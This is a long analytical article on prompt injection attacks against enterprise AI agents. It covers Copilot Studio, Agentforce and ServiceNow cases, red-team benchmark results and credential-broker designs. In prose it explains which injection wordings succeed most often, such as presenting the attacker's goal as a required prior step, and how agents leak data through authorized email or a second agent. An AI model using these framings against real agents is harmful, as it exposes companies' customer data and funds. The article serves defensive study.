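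VentureBeat's *Microsoft patched a Copilot Studio prompt injection. The data exfiltrated anyway* (2026) describes the test. Capsule's comment imitated a system message, the part of a model's input where the developer puts standing instructions. Copilot Studio joined the comment to the agent's real instructions without filtering it, and the model followed it. The agent searched its connected SharePoint lists for customer data and sent the results to an outside address through Outlook. According to CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026), the data included names, addresses and phone numbers.

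Microsoft's safety mechanisms flagged the request as suspicious, but the agent sent the email anyway. Data loss prevention software, which is meant to stop confidential information from leaving a company, did not trigger, because the agent used an Outlook action that the system treated as authorized.

Microsoft confirmed the flaw on 5 December and patched it on 15 January 2026. A week later it published an entry in CVE, the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. The CVE Program's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) rates the severity at 7.5 out of 10 and notes that an attack requires no login or user action. Microsoft classified the flaw as command injection, a category for programs that let outside input alter a command, which fits the way Copilot Studio mixed the comment with the instructions. Microsoft could instead keep form text in a separate, lower-priority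 part of the input, but a model may still follow instructions it finds there, for the reasons David C gives.

Neither the CVE entry nor the press reports explain what the patch changed. CSO Online reports only that Microsoft made the fix internally and that customers did not need to act. In VentureBeat's title, "exfiltrated anyway" means that data was exfiltrated despite the safety warning in Capsule's test, though it could be misread as saying that the patch failed. The article reports no test of the patched product.

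### Closing one way out

Experience with similar products suggests that a patch may close one route for leaking data and leave others open. In September 2025 the security company Noma disclosed a way to leak data from Agentforce, Salesforce's agent product. Salesforce responded by restricting the web addresses to which an agent could send data. Capsule then found that an agent could send the data by email instead. Capsule planted text in a public form for prospective customers. When an employee asked the agent to review the submission, the agent retrieved other customer records and emailed them out. Capsule's chief executive, Naor Paz, told VentureBeat that the testers found no limit on how many records the agent would leak.

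Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read an employee's emails, chats and files, has a similar history. Microsoft patched a leak called EchoLeak in June 2025. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) describes three new ways to extract data from Copilot with a malicious email, which the victim doesn't have to open. The data could leave through the address of an image, a link to a saved file, or code that the assistant ran, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026). Microsoft had documented that the environment for running code blocked outbound traffic, but the block failed. Microsoft patched all three routes between September and November 2026.

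A more general remedy is to restrict what the agent can send. CISO Whisperer's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026) recommends limiting or reviewing outgoing email when an agent is acting on untrusted input, and VentureBeat suggests allowing email only to company addresses. Allowing only company addresses would have stopped the ShareLeak email, and it would barely limit an agent that only has to notify staff about new submissions.

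Restricting which addresses an agent can write to is much less useful when the agent replies to customers. A company might let such an agent write only to the address given on the form, but in this attack the attacker filled in the form. The agent would also need a limit on which records it could read while handling that submission. If it could open only that customer's record, it would have much less to send.

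### Whose permissions the agent uses

Microsoft's documentation suggests that the agent in ShareLeak read the lists with its builder's permissions, although press accounts do not specify whose permissions it used. The outsider had no permission to read them. A form submission starts an agent through an event trigger, and Microsoft states that these triggers can use only the builder's credentials. Builders receive a warning about this before they publish the agent, according to Microsoft's *Add an event trigger*. Microsoft's training material states that an agent started by a user's message can instead use that user's authentication.

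Running an agent with its builder's permissions is risky even without prompt injection. Suppose a manager builds an agent that can open salary reports and shares it with the whole department. An intern who can't open the reports directly may get their contents by asking the agent. Microsoft warns of this "oversharing", in which users obtain data or perform actions that only the builder's account allows. Hardy's compiler had the same fault, since it used its own license to write to a file that the user could not open.

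A company can reduce the damage by giving the agent a service account, which belongs to software instead of a person. The account needs only the permissions for the agent's job, whereas a builder's personal account usually has all the permissions the builder's own work requires. But everyone who can influence the agent still shares the service account's permissions.

If the agent uses the current user's credentials, the service refuses the intern's request just as it would if the intern had made it directly. This is an improvement, but it limits only what users can get by asking the agent. When a manager asks the agent to process a document and the agent follows an instruction planted in it, the agent acts with the manager's permissions.

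| Authority the agent uses | What a user can obtain by asking | What planted text can reach | Work with no user present |
|---|---|---|---|
| Builder's account | Whatever the builder's account and the agent's tools allow | The same | Possible |
| Service account | Whatever that account and the agent's tools allow | The same | Possible |
| Current user's account | Only what that user may do | Whatever the current user may do through the agent's tools | Needs a way to authorize later use of the account |

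By default, Copilot Studio lets builders choose whether an agent uses their own credentials or the user's. According to a Microsoft notice reproduced by itelio, from 25 August 2026 administrators can block the use of builders' credentials, but the restriction is off unless they turn it on. When they do, every affected agent immediately starts asking users to sign in, and agents that run in the background fail.

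A preview that began on 30 July 2026 offers a way around this. It lets builders create triggers that run in the background with an end user's credentials, according to another notice reproduced by itelio. In the ShareLeak case, the agent would then use the permissions of the employee it ran for instead of the builder's. The attacker would get less if that employee could see fewer customer records, but would still be using the form to direct an agent with permissions that the attacker did not have.

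### A ticket that enlisted a second agent

In the ServiceNow attack, the agent uses the current user's permissions. Companies use ServiceNow to manage requests and problems as tickets, and Now Assist adds agents that can process those tickets. Aaron Costello described the attack in November 2025, when he was chief of security research at AppOmni, which sells security tools for business software.

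Costello deployed two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents where only an administrator could use them. One read incident tickets and categorised them. The other could read, create and update records in a large group of tables. He also created a low-privilege account that could submit tickets but not read anyone else's.

From this account, he submitted a ticket numbered INC0000002. In its description, he wrote that any agent reading the ticket had to copy the description of another ticket, INC0000001, into this one before it could complete its task. He instructed any agent that could not do this itself to look for other agents that could.

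When the administrator had an agent process the ticket, Now Assist found the more powerful agent, and the confidential text was copied into the low-privileged user's own ticket, where that user could read it. ServiceNow's prompt injection protection was on throughout. Restricting outgoing email would not have helped, because the information never left ServiceNow.

Now Assist agents run with the permissions of whoever started the interaction, unless the company configures them otherwise. The second agent therefore had the administrator's permissions, so ServiceNow's access rules correctly allowed it to read INC0000001. The same rules had blocked the ticket's author from reading that record directly. Costello calls this second-order prompt injection, because the attacker stores an instruction that takes effect when another user's agent later reads it.

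In other tests he got agents to send records by email and to give a malicious user the administrator role. The role change is a particularly serious misuse of the agent's grant because it gives the attacker a new grant of their own, so they no longer need the agent.

### Settings that limit the second agent

Three default settings let Now Assist agents find and use each other. The default language model supports discovering other agents, agents published in the same place join the same team, and publishing an agent makes it discoverable. AppOmni recommends dividing agents into teams that each contain only the agents one task requires. If the categorising agent had been in its own team, it could not have found the agent that updated records. Separating the agents limits the actions available after the model follows the planted instruction, but does not prevent the model from following it.

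AppOmni also recommends supervised mode for tools that change records or send email, so that a user must review each action first. The system property sn_aia.enable_usecase_tool_execution_mode_override is "false" by default. If an administrator sets it to "true", any agent with at least one autonomous tool runs all its tools without supervision.

Supervision works only if the administrator notices the problem. An administrator processing INC0000002 might see a request to update it as routine, unless the screen also shows that the new text came from a different ticket. Paz objects more broadly to Salesforce's similar recommendation, arguing that an agent whose every operation needs approval is "not really an agent". His company sells an automated alternative, and his objection is weaker when only operations that could do serious harm need approval.

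ServiceNow told Costello that the agents' behaviour was intended, and it clarified its documentation. Costello similarly called the result "expected behavior" under certain default settings, not a bug in the AI (The Hacker News, 2025). Salesforce also described the email route in its product as "configuration-specific", whereas Microsoft treated ShareLeak as a vulnerability. Microsoft's patch protected its customers without their having to do anything, but ServiceNow's customers have to find out about the settings and change them.

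Another rule could limit the agent to actions that both the administrator and the ticket's author may perform. It would have stopped the copying, because the author had no permission to read INC0000001. But it could also stop the agent from categorising tickets if ordinary users may not set the category. The rule would restrict an agent that handles a public web form even more, because an anonymous visitor usually has no permissions inside the company. Companies use agents partly to do things that people cannot do for themselves, such as routing a complaint to the right department.

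### How a limit disappears in a handover

Work often passes through several agents before one of them acts. Surapani and colleagues describe a hierarchy in which authority passes from a user, through the organisation that runs the system, to a main agent and then to more specialised agents, which call the tools. They distinguish this path of authority from the path of information. A ticketing system belongs to both, because an agent needs permission to use it and may also read an attacker's instructions there. Any decision to allow an action should therefore consider both who granted the permission and whose text prompted the action.

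In the invoice-summary case, the read-only limit is lost when the main agent hands the work to a finance agent, perhaps with a message such as "deal with these invoices". If the limit existed only in the main agent's instructions or choice of tools, the message does not pass it on to the finance agent, which still has its own credential for payments.

Preserving the limit means sending it along with the work in a form that software can enforce. Let *C*ᵢ be the authority available at step *i*, and let *L*ᵢ₊₁ be the set of operations that the next step needs. At each handover, the system calculates

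*C*ᵢ₊₁ = *C*ᵢ ∩ *L*ᵢ₊₁

The next agent receives only the permissions in both sets, so authority can never grow, as Gallo's rule requires. In the summary case, *C*₀ contains permission to read the invoices but not to pay them. The intersection therefore excludes payments, even if the finance agent usually makes them.

The main agent's software could do this by obtaining a read-only token and passing it to the finance agent, which must then use that token for the job. If the finance agent's software can fall back on its own payment credential when the read-only token fails, the restriction accomplishes nothing. An agent that works for several people must also keep their permissions separate, or an instruction in one person's task could make it use authority granted for another's.

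In the ServiceNow attack, the result of the calculation depends on the initial permissions, *C*₀. If *C*₀ contains everything the administrator may do, and the system passes all of it on, every handover obeys the rule but the attack still works. If *C*₀ contains only permission to read INC0000002 and set its category, the software would refuse to let the second agent read INC0000001 or change the description of INC0000002, even though the administrator has permission to do both.

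Someone has to choose this narrow starting point before the agent reads the ticket. If the model chose it afterwards, the planted text could cause it to include INC0000001. This is fairly easy for an agent that only categorises tickets, because its builder can write the limit once and fill in the ticket number each time. It is much harder for a general assistant, whose user may ask for almost anything.

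Shrinking authority would help only a little in the invoice example. Suppose the main agent delegates the job to a payment agent that is allowed to make only one payment of up to $4,200. The attacker can no longer use the rest of the $10,000 limit or get a second payment from the same task. But the payment agent's permission still covers the payment to A-999, unless it also limits the payee to S-100.

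### What the gap analysis compared

Surapani and colleagues derive seven requirements for authorizing agents and rate existing mechanisms' coverage of them as strong, partial or absent. The mechanisms are traditional access control, capabilities, identity management systems, and newer frameworks designed for agents. They selected their 89 sources from about 180 candidates published between 2023 and 2026. They also apply the requirements to three sets of software a company could deploy today, and trace one refused request from the user's instruction to the audit record.

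This comparison covers documented designs, so it can show that a control is missing, but not how well a control works once a company has configured it or how often attacks succeed against working systems. In AppOmni's test, for example, the attack succeeded with a ServiceNow protection against prompt injection turned on.

The review identifies two main gaps: enforcement when an agent calls a tool, and "aggregation bounds", which limit what an agent can accumulate over many actions. The Agentforce leak shows why such limits matter. An employee reviewing a prospective customer may have good reason to look up another customer's record, but hardly ever needs to email the whole database to a stranger.

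### Demonstrations and real attacks

The evidence for both attacks comes from researchers' tests. In the CVE entry for ShareLeak, the US cybersecurity agency CISA lists exploitation as "none". A copy of Microsoft's advisory data in STAR Labs' *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) gives the status as "Not Exploited". Costello set up the ServiceNow agents and the low-privileged account himself. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* (2025) describes an earlier Copilot Studio attack by the security company Zenity, which used a replica of an agent built by the consulting firm McKinsey. Cato, Simonovich's employer, knows of no real attacks using its three Copilot routes.

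The OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks* (2026), an AI-generated entry in its incident monitor, states that attackers exploited the Microsoft and Salesforce flaws. This appears to be a misreading of Capsule's demonstrations as real thefts, since the OECD entry identifies no victim and the CVE entry does not support the claim.

Companies use prompt injection outside the laboratory. Microsoft found more than 50 distinct prompts meant to bias the recommendations of AI assistants, from 31 companies. These prompts did not use anyone's authorization to take data or change records.

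The lack of reported thefts is weaker evidence that none occurred than it would be for many other kinds of attack. CISA made its assessment on 24 January 2026, nearly three months before Capsule published its account. Misuse of an agent's valid authorization also leaves records that look much like ordinary work, such as an email sent by an agent that is allowed to send email. In Capsule's Salesforce test, the employee who started the agent received no sign that data had left the company.

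VentureBeat advises companies that used Copilot Studio agents with SharePoint forms to look for signs of an attack between 24 November 2025 and 15 January 2026. Capsule found the flaw on the first of these dates, but someone else could have found it earlier. So a more careful search would begin on the day the company connected its agent to the form, and would compare each outgoing email with the submission that prompted it.

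## Red-team tests: how often models obey instructions that fit the task

The attacks on GitHub, Copilot Studio and ServiceNow show that models can follow planted instructions, but not how often they do. Researchers estimate the rate with red-team tests, in which they attack an agent in a simulated environment. Published rates range from zero to 100%, depending on the model, the wording of the planted text, the number of attempts, and whether the researchers count attempted or completed actions.

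### How AgentDojo scores an attack

*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) has four simulated environments, for office work, the messaging service Slack, travel booking and banking. Each has tools and stored data that the tools can read or change, such as an inbox or an account balance. A user task is an ordinary request, such as paying the bill in a particular file. An injection task is the attacker's goal, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account. The researchers plant an instruction to carry out the injection task somewhere the agent will look during the user task, such as an email or a web page.

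When the agent stops, the researchers' code checks whether it completed the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal. They chose fixed code over a language model because an injection that takes over the agent might also take over a model judging it. They also report how often the agent completes the user's task while under attack, since an agent that refused every request would never obey an attacker.

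They pair each user task with each injection task in the same environment, which gives 629 test cases:

40 × 6 + 21 × 5 + 20 × 7 + 16 × 9 = 629

AgentDojo has since grown to more than 900 combinations, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026). Researchers can also give the agent an injection task as if it were the user's own request. If the agent can't complete the task even then, its failure to complete it under attack is poor evidence that it resisted the injection.

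AgentDojo's attack success rate is the share of test cases in which the agent completes the attacker's goal. Against GPT-4o, a leading model at the time, the rate was 47.7% when the planted message addressed the model and the user by their correct names. Using the wrong name for the user roughly halved the rate. Attacks succeeded most often when the message said that the agent had to do another task before the original one. This wording was clearly more effective than "ignore previous instructions". Counting an attack as successful if any of four wordings worked raised the rate by another 10%.

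Counting an attack as successful only when the agent completes the attacker's whole goal can hide partial obedience. One travel injection told the agent to book the most expensive hotel in Paris and email the user's personal information to the attacker. The agent often did one of these but never both, so the attack scored 0%. A weak model can also appear secure because it tries to follow the attacker's instruction but fails to carry it out. Debenedetti and colleagues offer this as a reason why the more capable models of 2024 tended to be easier to attack.

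They also tried a form of tool gating in which the agent chose its tools before reading any untrusted text. This lowered the rate to 7.5%, mostly because many user tasks only required reading, while the attacker needed to send or change something. But in 17% of the test cases, the tools for the user's task were also enough to carry out the attack. The invoice example belongs in this group because the agent needs the payment tool for the legitimate payment.

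### Crude and task-aligned instructions

An attacker can make an instruction more persuasive by presenting the harmful action as a step in the user's task. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, summarizes a benchmark that compares such task-aligned injections with crude requests for the same action. The tests run in a sandbox that prevents real harm, so the attack success rate counts attempts. An attack succeeds if the model issues an unauthorized tool call or reproduces a marker planted as evidence. Outside a sandbox, the attempted call would run unless something checked it first. The paper found no default check of the values in each call in three agent toolkits.

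| Model | Crude wording | Task-aligned wording |
|---|---|---|
| glm-4.7 | 0.283 | 1.000 |
| gemma-3-12b-it | 0.000 | 0.571 |
| mistral-large | 0.027 | 0.459 |
| Latam-GPT, English | 0.320 | 0.520 |
| Latam-GPT, Spanish | 0.240 | 0.040 |

glm-4.7 attempted the action in 13 of 46 trials with the crude wording and in all 46 with the wording that fit the task. The increases for gemma-3-12b-it and mistral-large are also too large to be due to chance. Gemma's result is the most worrying for anyone who relies on a simple test, because a tester who used only the crude wording would have concluded that the model was immune.

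With Latam-GPT, a Latin American model built on Llama 3.1, the task-aligned wording worked more often in English, but a paired analysis did not rule out chance (*p* = 0.096). In Spanish it worked *less* often, and chance is an unlikely explanation (*p* = 0.004). The model may resist this wording better in Spanish, or it may have produced more tool calls that the test software could not read, because Mellafe Zuvic ran a compressed version that had to write its calls as ordinary text. In a separate Spanish test with a pretext about payment card security, the same model attempted an unauthorized payout in ten out of ten trials, which makes a general resistance in Spanish unlikely.

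A separate comparison tested 27 models with the task-aligned wording. On average, the 12 low-cost models attempted the attacker's action in 60.3% of trials, compared with 18.9% for the 15 flagships, the developers' most capable models. The groups overlap because some flagships also had high rates. Two low-cost models, gpt-4o-mini and glm-4.5-air, attempted the action in every trial. The flagship glm-5.2 did so in 8.7% of trials, and gemini-3.1-pro-preview, also a flagship, never did. Mellafe Zuvic gives no confidence interval for the difference between the groups.

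The gap matters because companies have a reason to use cheap models for high-volume work such as processing email, although the study has no data on which models they run. In another test, Mellafe Zuvic imitated business email compromise, a fraud in which someone poses as a supplier or colleague to redirect a payment. Both gpt-4o-mini and glm-4.5-air attempted the unauthorized payout in all ten of their trials. This test is the closest to the invoice example, and it suggests that an agent running on either model would probably pay A-999.

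One person wrote all the scenarios in the paired benchmark, and each has a single turn and delivers the injection in the same way. The size of the increase therefore depends partly on how well that person wrote the blunt requests, and better ones might have narrowed the gap. The direction is easier to believe because AgentDojo's most effective message also presented the attacker's task as something the agent had to do before the user's task.

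The flagship models' greater resistance reverses the pattern that AgentDojo found in 2024, when more capable models tended to be easier to attack. A likely reason is that developers have since trained their best models to resist injections.

### Why a fitting request is hard to reject

A crude injection usually asks for something unrelated to the task, and a model or filter can detect the mismatch. For example, an agent summarizing a calendar has no reason to email someone a security code. The email in the invoice example contains no such mismatch, because suppliers do change banks and a genuine notice could use exactly the same words.

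A filter that instead blocked every instruction from anyone but the user would also block legitimate work, because many tasks consist of carrying out such instructions, including AgentDojo's request to pay the bill in a file. A newer benchmark, AgentDyn, deliberately includes helpful instructions from third parties, according to *StepGuard* (2026), so an agent that ignores them all will fail some legitimate tasks. Even in AgentDojo, a filter trained to detect injections raised so many false alarms that the agent completed far fewer user tasks.

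Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a February 2026 test in which one of the company's researchers tricked an employee into giving a prompt to Claude Code, its coding agent. The prompt looked like routine setup instructions, but one step was to send cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. The user had supplied the text, so Claude had no reason to doubt where it came from. This makes the test a *direct* injection, and its rate is not comparable with those for planted emails. Still, the result suggests that a model's resistance depends heavily on recognising that an instruction does not come from the user, and wording that fits the task makes this harder.

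When a model is unsure, it can ask the user. If the agent noticed that A-999 was new and asked the user to confirm it with the supplier, it would stop the fraud without rejecting genuine changes. Developers can train models to do this, but an agent that asks about every unfamiliar detail will save its user much less time.

### What the strongest models achieve

Anthropic's best models have much lower rates than the averages above. On an Agent Red Teaming benchmark from the security company Gray Swan, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time with a single attempt and 5 to 6% of the time when the attacker had 100 attempts and could adapt to earlier failures.

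Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, a model released in September, reports results on a different Gray Swan benchmark, made specifically for indirect injections. The benchmark has 37 scenarios, including data theft and unintended payments, and 1,804 attacks from public competitions. The attack success rate against Fable 5.1 was 0.1% after one attempt, 0.7% after 10 and 1.0% after 15, compared with 0.4%, 3.6% and 4.8% for Claude Opus 5. Most of the successful attacks on Fable 5.1 involved computer use, where the agent operates programs by looking at the screen.

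Those attacks are hard to resist, but they were not tailored to the models tested. Gray Swan selected attacks that worked against several models, and Anthropic reports results only for models that competitors had not targeted, because attacks tailored to a model make it look worse than its rivals. This makes the comparison fair, but 15 attempts from a ready-made collection do not measure how well an attacker could do with a message tailored to Fable 5.1. On the other hand, Gray Swan tested the Claude models without the additional protections against injection that Anthropic's products use, so those products may do better than the model alone.

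The choice of attacks can change the result substantially. When Anthropic released Opus 5, it reported an attack success rate of 2.0% after 15 attempts, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. By September, the reported rate for the same model was 4.8% on a version of the benchmark with nine new scenarios and 670 new attacks. Fable 5's rate rose from 2.8% to 6.5%. The rates probably rose because the newer attacks were better, or better suited to these models, rather than because the models had become weaker.

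OpenAI's figures for indirect injection are higher, though its tests are different. In an August 2026 update, the three GPT-5.6 models had average failure rates of 2.94% to 3.77%, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*. GPT-5.6 Sol failed on only about 0.05% of *direct* attacks, in which a user tries to override the developer's instructions. Citing only this lower rate would greatly understate the risk from a planted email. OpenAI has since reported that new training made GPT-6 Astra significantly more robust to jailbreaks, but jailbreaks are also attempts by users to get around a model's rules.

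### Small rates over many attempts

If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, and attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is

*P* = 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

At a success rate of 0.1% per attempt, an attacker has a 9.5% chance of at least one success in 100 attempts and a 63% chance in 1,000. The chance passes 50% at the 693rd attempt. At GPT-5.6 Sol's rate of 3.77%, 100 attempts would give a 98% chance.

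The formula assumes that attempts are independent, which is doubtful, and the published results for repeated attempts are lower than it predicts. The table includes older figures for Claude Opus 4.5, from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, and for Claude Opus 4.6 in a graphical interface without safeguards, from VentureBeat.

| Model | Rate for one attempt | Number of attempts | Predicted if independent | Reported |
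|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38.2% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99.2% | 63% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 17.8% | 200 | over 99.9% | 78.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | about 0.1% | 100 | 9.5% | 5–6% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 15 | 5.8% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 15 | 1.5% | 1.0% |

(Rounding could account for the gaps in the rows for Opus 4.7 and Fable 5.1, but not for the others.)

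One reason for the gap is that some situations are much easier to attack than others. Opus 4.6, for example, resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. Let *q* be the chance of success in a particular scenario, and let E denote the average over all scenarios. Then

E[1 − (1 − *q*)ⁿ] ≤ 1 − (1 − E[*q*])ⁿ

In the extreme case where an attack always works in 1% of scenarios and never in the rest, its average success rate is 1% after one attempt per scenario and still 1% after a hundred. Repeating the same message is especially unlikely to help at temperature 0, a setting where the model chooses its most likely output each time and so usually responds the same way.

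Real attackers can also do better than the formula predicts. They can learn from each failure, which raises their chance of success on the next attempt. If the victim uses a widely available agent, attackers can practise on their own copy until they find a message that works, then send only that one. A defence that looks for repeated failures would then have none to detect.

### Whether trained resistance is enough

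The case for relying on trained resistance is that attack success rates have fallen quickly and that developers can add other protections. With Anthropic's protective software turned on, no attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios, and The Decoder suggested that this might have solved prompt injection in browsers. One part of the software looks for planted instructions in incoming text, and another blocks dangerous actions before they run. Without the software, the success rate was 3.7%, so the model was not solely responsible for the result. If the 129 scenarios were a random sample of a larger set, attacks could still succeed in up to 2.3% of that set, at the 95% confidence level.

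Security specialists tend to set a stricter standard. In August 2025, Willison (2025) quoted the security researcher Bruce Schneier: "We have zero agentic AI systems that are secure against these attacks." Schneier wrote this before most of the improvements described above, and a model that fails once in a thousand attempts is far safer than the ones he had in mind. But it would not meet his standard, which is whether an attacker can succeed at all. Anthropic does not rely on trained resistance alone either, and writes that its model-level defences are strong but "can't stand alone".

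Even a small remaining success rate can matter because, as Anthropic points out, an attacker can send the same email to a thousand inboxes. Suppose a thousand companies use agents like the one in the invoice example, and each receives one false invoice for $4,200. At a rate of 0.1%, the attacker would receive one payment on average. At 60.3%, the mean for the low-cost models, the average would be 603 payments, or about $2.5 million. These averages are the same whether or not the agents' failures are correlated.

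Trained resistance would therefore cut the attacker's expected income by a factor of about 600. That might make the fraud unprofitable if each invoice took substantial research into a company's suppliers, but it would be less of a deterrent if another agent could write the invoices for a few cents each.

A single company can reasonably require only that an agent do better than human clerks, who sometimes pay false invoices. But across many companies, a thousand agents that run on one model might all misread the same email in the same way, which a thousand clerks would not do. Most messages would then fail everywhere, and an occasional one would succeed at many companies on the same day.

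## Credential brokers: hiding the key from the agent

Even the best models sometimes follow planted instructions, so developers also try to limit what an attacker gains when that happens. A common measure is a credential broker, which either adds the credentials to the agent's requests itself or issues short-lived substitutes. A broker protects well against theft but much less against misuse, because the agent must still be able to use the key even though it can't see it.

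### Vercel: adding the key as a request leaves

Agents that write and run programs make credentials easy to steal. *Security boundaries in agentic architectures* (Ubl and Arora, 2026), published by the cloud company Vercel, describes an agent that reads a server log while investigating a fault. An attacker has planted a comment in the log claiming that the billing service has moved and giving a command that supposedly tests the connection. If the agent runs the command in an environment that holds the machine's login key and cloud credentials, the command uploads both to the attacker's server.

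Vercel's remedy is to run such programs in a sandbox, an isolated virtual machine, and to keep the keys outside it. Tuttle (2026), in *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox*, describes how a request gets its credential:

1. A program in the sandbox sends a request that contains no key.
2. The request passes through a firewall on the host machine, which nothing in the sandbox can change or switch off. The firewall reads the name of the destination and checks it against a list.
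3. If the developer has configured a credential for that destination, the firewall decrypts the request. It can do so because the sandbox trusts a certificate authority that the firewall created for this sandbox alone.
4. The firewall adds the credential, replacing any that the program supplied under the same header name.
5. It opens a new encrypted connection to the service and sends the request on.

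The program receives the reply as if it had logged in itself. Cloudflare (2026) offers the same arrangement. In its example, a sandbox authenticates any request an agent makes to GitHub, but the agent can never read the credential.

### Anthropic: a vault behind a proxy

Managed Agents is Anthropic's service for running agents on long tasks. In its first version, the code that Claude wrote ran in the same container as the credentials, so an injection "only had to convince Claude to read its own environment", according to Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents*. Anthropic then moved the model and the software that runs its tool loop out of the container, and made the credentials inaccessible to the code running inside it.

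For Git, the standard tool for sharing code, the service uses the repository's access token once, at start-up, to copy the code into the sandbox and connect the copy to the original. Claude can then fetch and push changes without handling the token. (Git often stores such a token in a plain file beside the code. Anthropic states that the sandbox cannot reach its tokens, but does not explain how the Git arrangement ensures this.)

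Other tools go through a proxy. When Claude calls an MCP tool, the proxy receives a token that identifies the session, uses it to find the matching OAuth token in a vault, and calls the outside service. Even the software that runs the tool loop never holds the OAuth token.

Many command-line programs expect to find their key in the sandbox's settings. Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* explains that, for these programs, the sandbox holds a placeholder and the service swaps in the real key as the request leaves. Developers can restrict the swap to particular destinations.

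The placeholder leaves two gaps. First, if a program uses the key to obtain a temporary session token, that token comes back into the sandbox unconcealed. Second, by default the service replaces the placeholder in the body of a request as well as in its headers. An attacker could therefore inject an instruction to write the placeholder into a shared document at a permitted service, and the document would contain the real key. Anthropic calls the body the broader exposure surface, and developers can limit the replacement to headers.

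### Three models in the Credential Broker for Agents draft

*Credential Broker for Agents (CB4A)* (Hartman, 2026), a draft written at the security training organisation SANS, separates the decision to grant access from the handling of keys. The agent submits a signed request that specifies the service, action, resource, duration and reason. In Hartman's example, the agent asks for permission to post in one Slack channel for 60 seconds. A policy component with no access to any credential approves or refuses the request. A second component can reach the credentials but may act only on a signed approval, so an attacker who breaks into one component does not automatically control the other.

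Hartman describes three ways of delivering the access:

| Model | What the agent receives | What an attacker could still steal from the agent |
|---|---|---|
| Proxy | A session token for the broker, which makes the call itself | No credential for the service |
| Short-lived token | A temporary token, valid for seconds to minutes, which the agent presents to the service | The temporary token |
| Delayed revocation | The real key, which the broker arranges to cancel after the task | The real key, which keeps working indefinitely if cancellation fails |

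Vercel's firewall and Anthropic's tool proxy both belong in the first row. Hartman prefers short-lived tokens because a proxy slows every call and stops everything if it fails. He reserves the proxy for services that cannot issue or check suitable tokens, and discourages delayed revocation except for old services that allow nothing else.

Hartman's draft has made little progress toward becoming a standard. Anyone can submit a draft to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), and as of August 2026 no working group had adopted Hartman's. It expired on 30 September, apparently without a second version or a formal successor. *Credential Delegation Protocol for AI Agents in Multi-System Environments* (Sweeney, 2026), a July draft, is the closest later work. It uses only the proxy model and adds rules for handing work from one agent to another. An IETF working group has meanwhile adopted a more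 general framework, *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization* (Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues, 2026). Hartman's draft is therefore more useful for understanding the options than for predicting what services will support.

### What the attacker loses

The case for hiding credentials is strong. Every program in the sandbox can access a key stored there, and Tuttle points out that a thief can keep using a copy long after the sandbox has stopped. If the firewall holds the key instead, uploading every file in the sandbox gives the attacker no access to the service, and the attacker can act only through the agent while it is running.

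A thief can also escape the limits the developer placed on the agent. Anthropic was concerned that an attacker with the agent's tokens could "spawn fresh, unrestricted sessions" and delegate work to them. An approval prompt in the original session would not stop work done in the new ones.

Hartman cites LiteLLM, a program that thousands of companies use to route requests to AI providers, as an example of large-scale credential theft. In March 2026, attackers put code that stole credentials into its published packages. They took an estimated 300 gigabytes of compressed credentials, affecting about 500,000 corporate identities. The attack didn't involve prompt injection, but the attackers could have stolen much less from machines that held no keys.

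The same incident is also a warning about brokers, because LiteLLM held keys for dozens of providers on behalf of other software, which is close to what a broker does. Hartman rates a break-in at the broker as the most severe threat to his design. His remedies include erasing each key from memory after use, but he accepts that an attacker inside the broker could still capture a key during use.

A narrow scope makes a stolen token less useful. Anthropic calls narrow scopes an obvious mitigation but does not rely on them, because choosing one means assuming what Claude cannot do with a limited token, "and Claude is getting increasingly smart". For example, a developer might grant permission to edit a build script without realising that the script runs with much wider permissions.

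A model might do unexpected damage even with a limited token, which is a good reason to hide the token as well as limit it. But an agent that never sees the token can usually do the same damage by sending the same requests through a proxy. Narrow scopes are therefore just as necessary when the token is hidden, and Tuttle recommends them for injected credentials too.

### Why misuse survives

Ubl and Arora write that their own proxy "doesn't prevent misuse during active runtime". The firewall attaches a key based on the request, chiefly its destination. It has no information about why the agent sent the request, so one prompted by a planted instruction gets the same key as any other. An HttpOnly cookie has the same weakness in a browser.

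In the Pacman attack, a proxy like Cloudflare's would have authenticated both the requests that read the private repositories and the request that published their contents. Similarly, an agent in a Managed Agents sandbox could push an attacker's code to a repository without handling the Git token. When several agents share a session, any agent whose definition includes the matching tool server can use the vault's credentials, and delegating a task to another agent does not by itself reduce what those credentials allow.

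#### Short lifetimes

Hartman, in *Your AI Agent Is an Easily Confused Deputy*, describes an agent that reads performance data from Amazon's cloud, queries a database, opens a ticket and notifies staff on Slack. Without a broker, the agent holds four long-lived credentials at once. With a broker, it requests each credential when needed, and the first is a read-only token that lasts 60 seconds. Hartman argues that an attacker who takes over the agent while it holds that first token has nothing else and cannot move on to the database, "because those credentials do not exist yet".

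That is true of an attacker who copies the token and leaves, but an attacker whose instructions remain in the agent's context can have the agent request the database token next, as it would have done anyway. The broker verifies that the request comes from the right software on the right machine. An injection changes neither, so the request would fail only if it broke one of the broker's policies or looked unusual.

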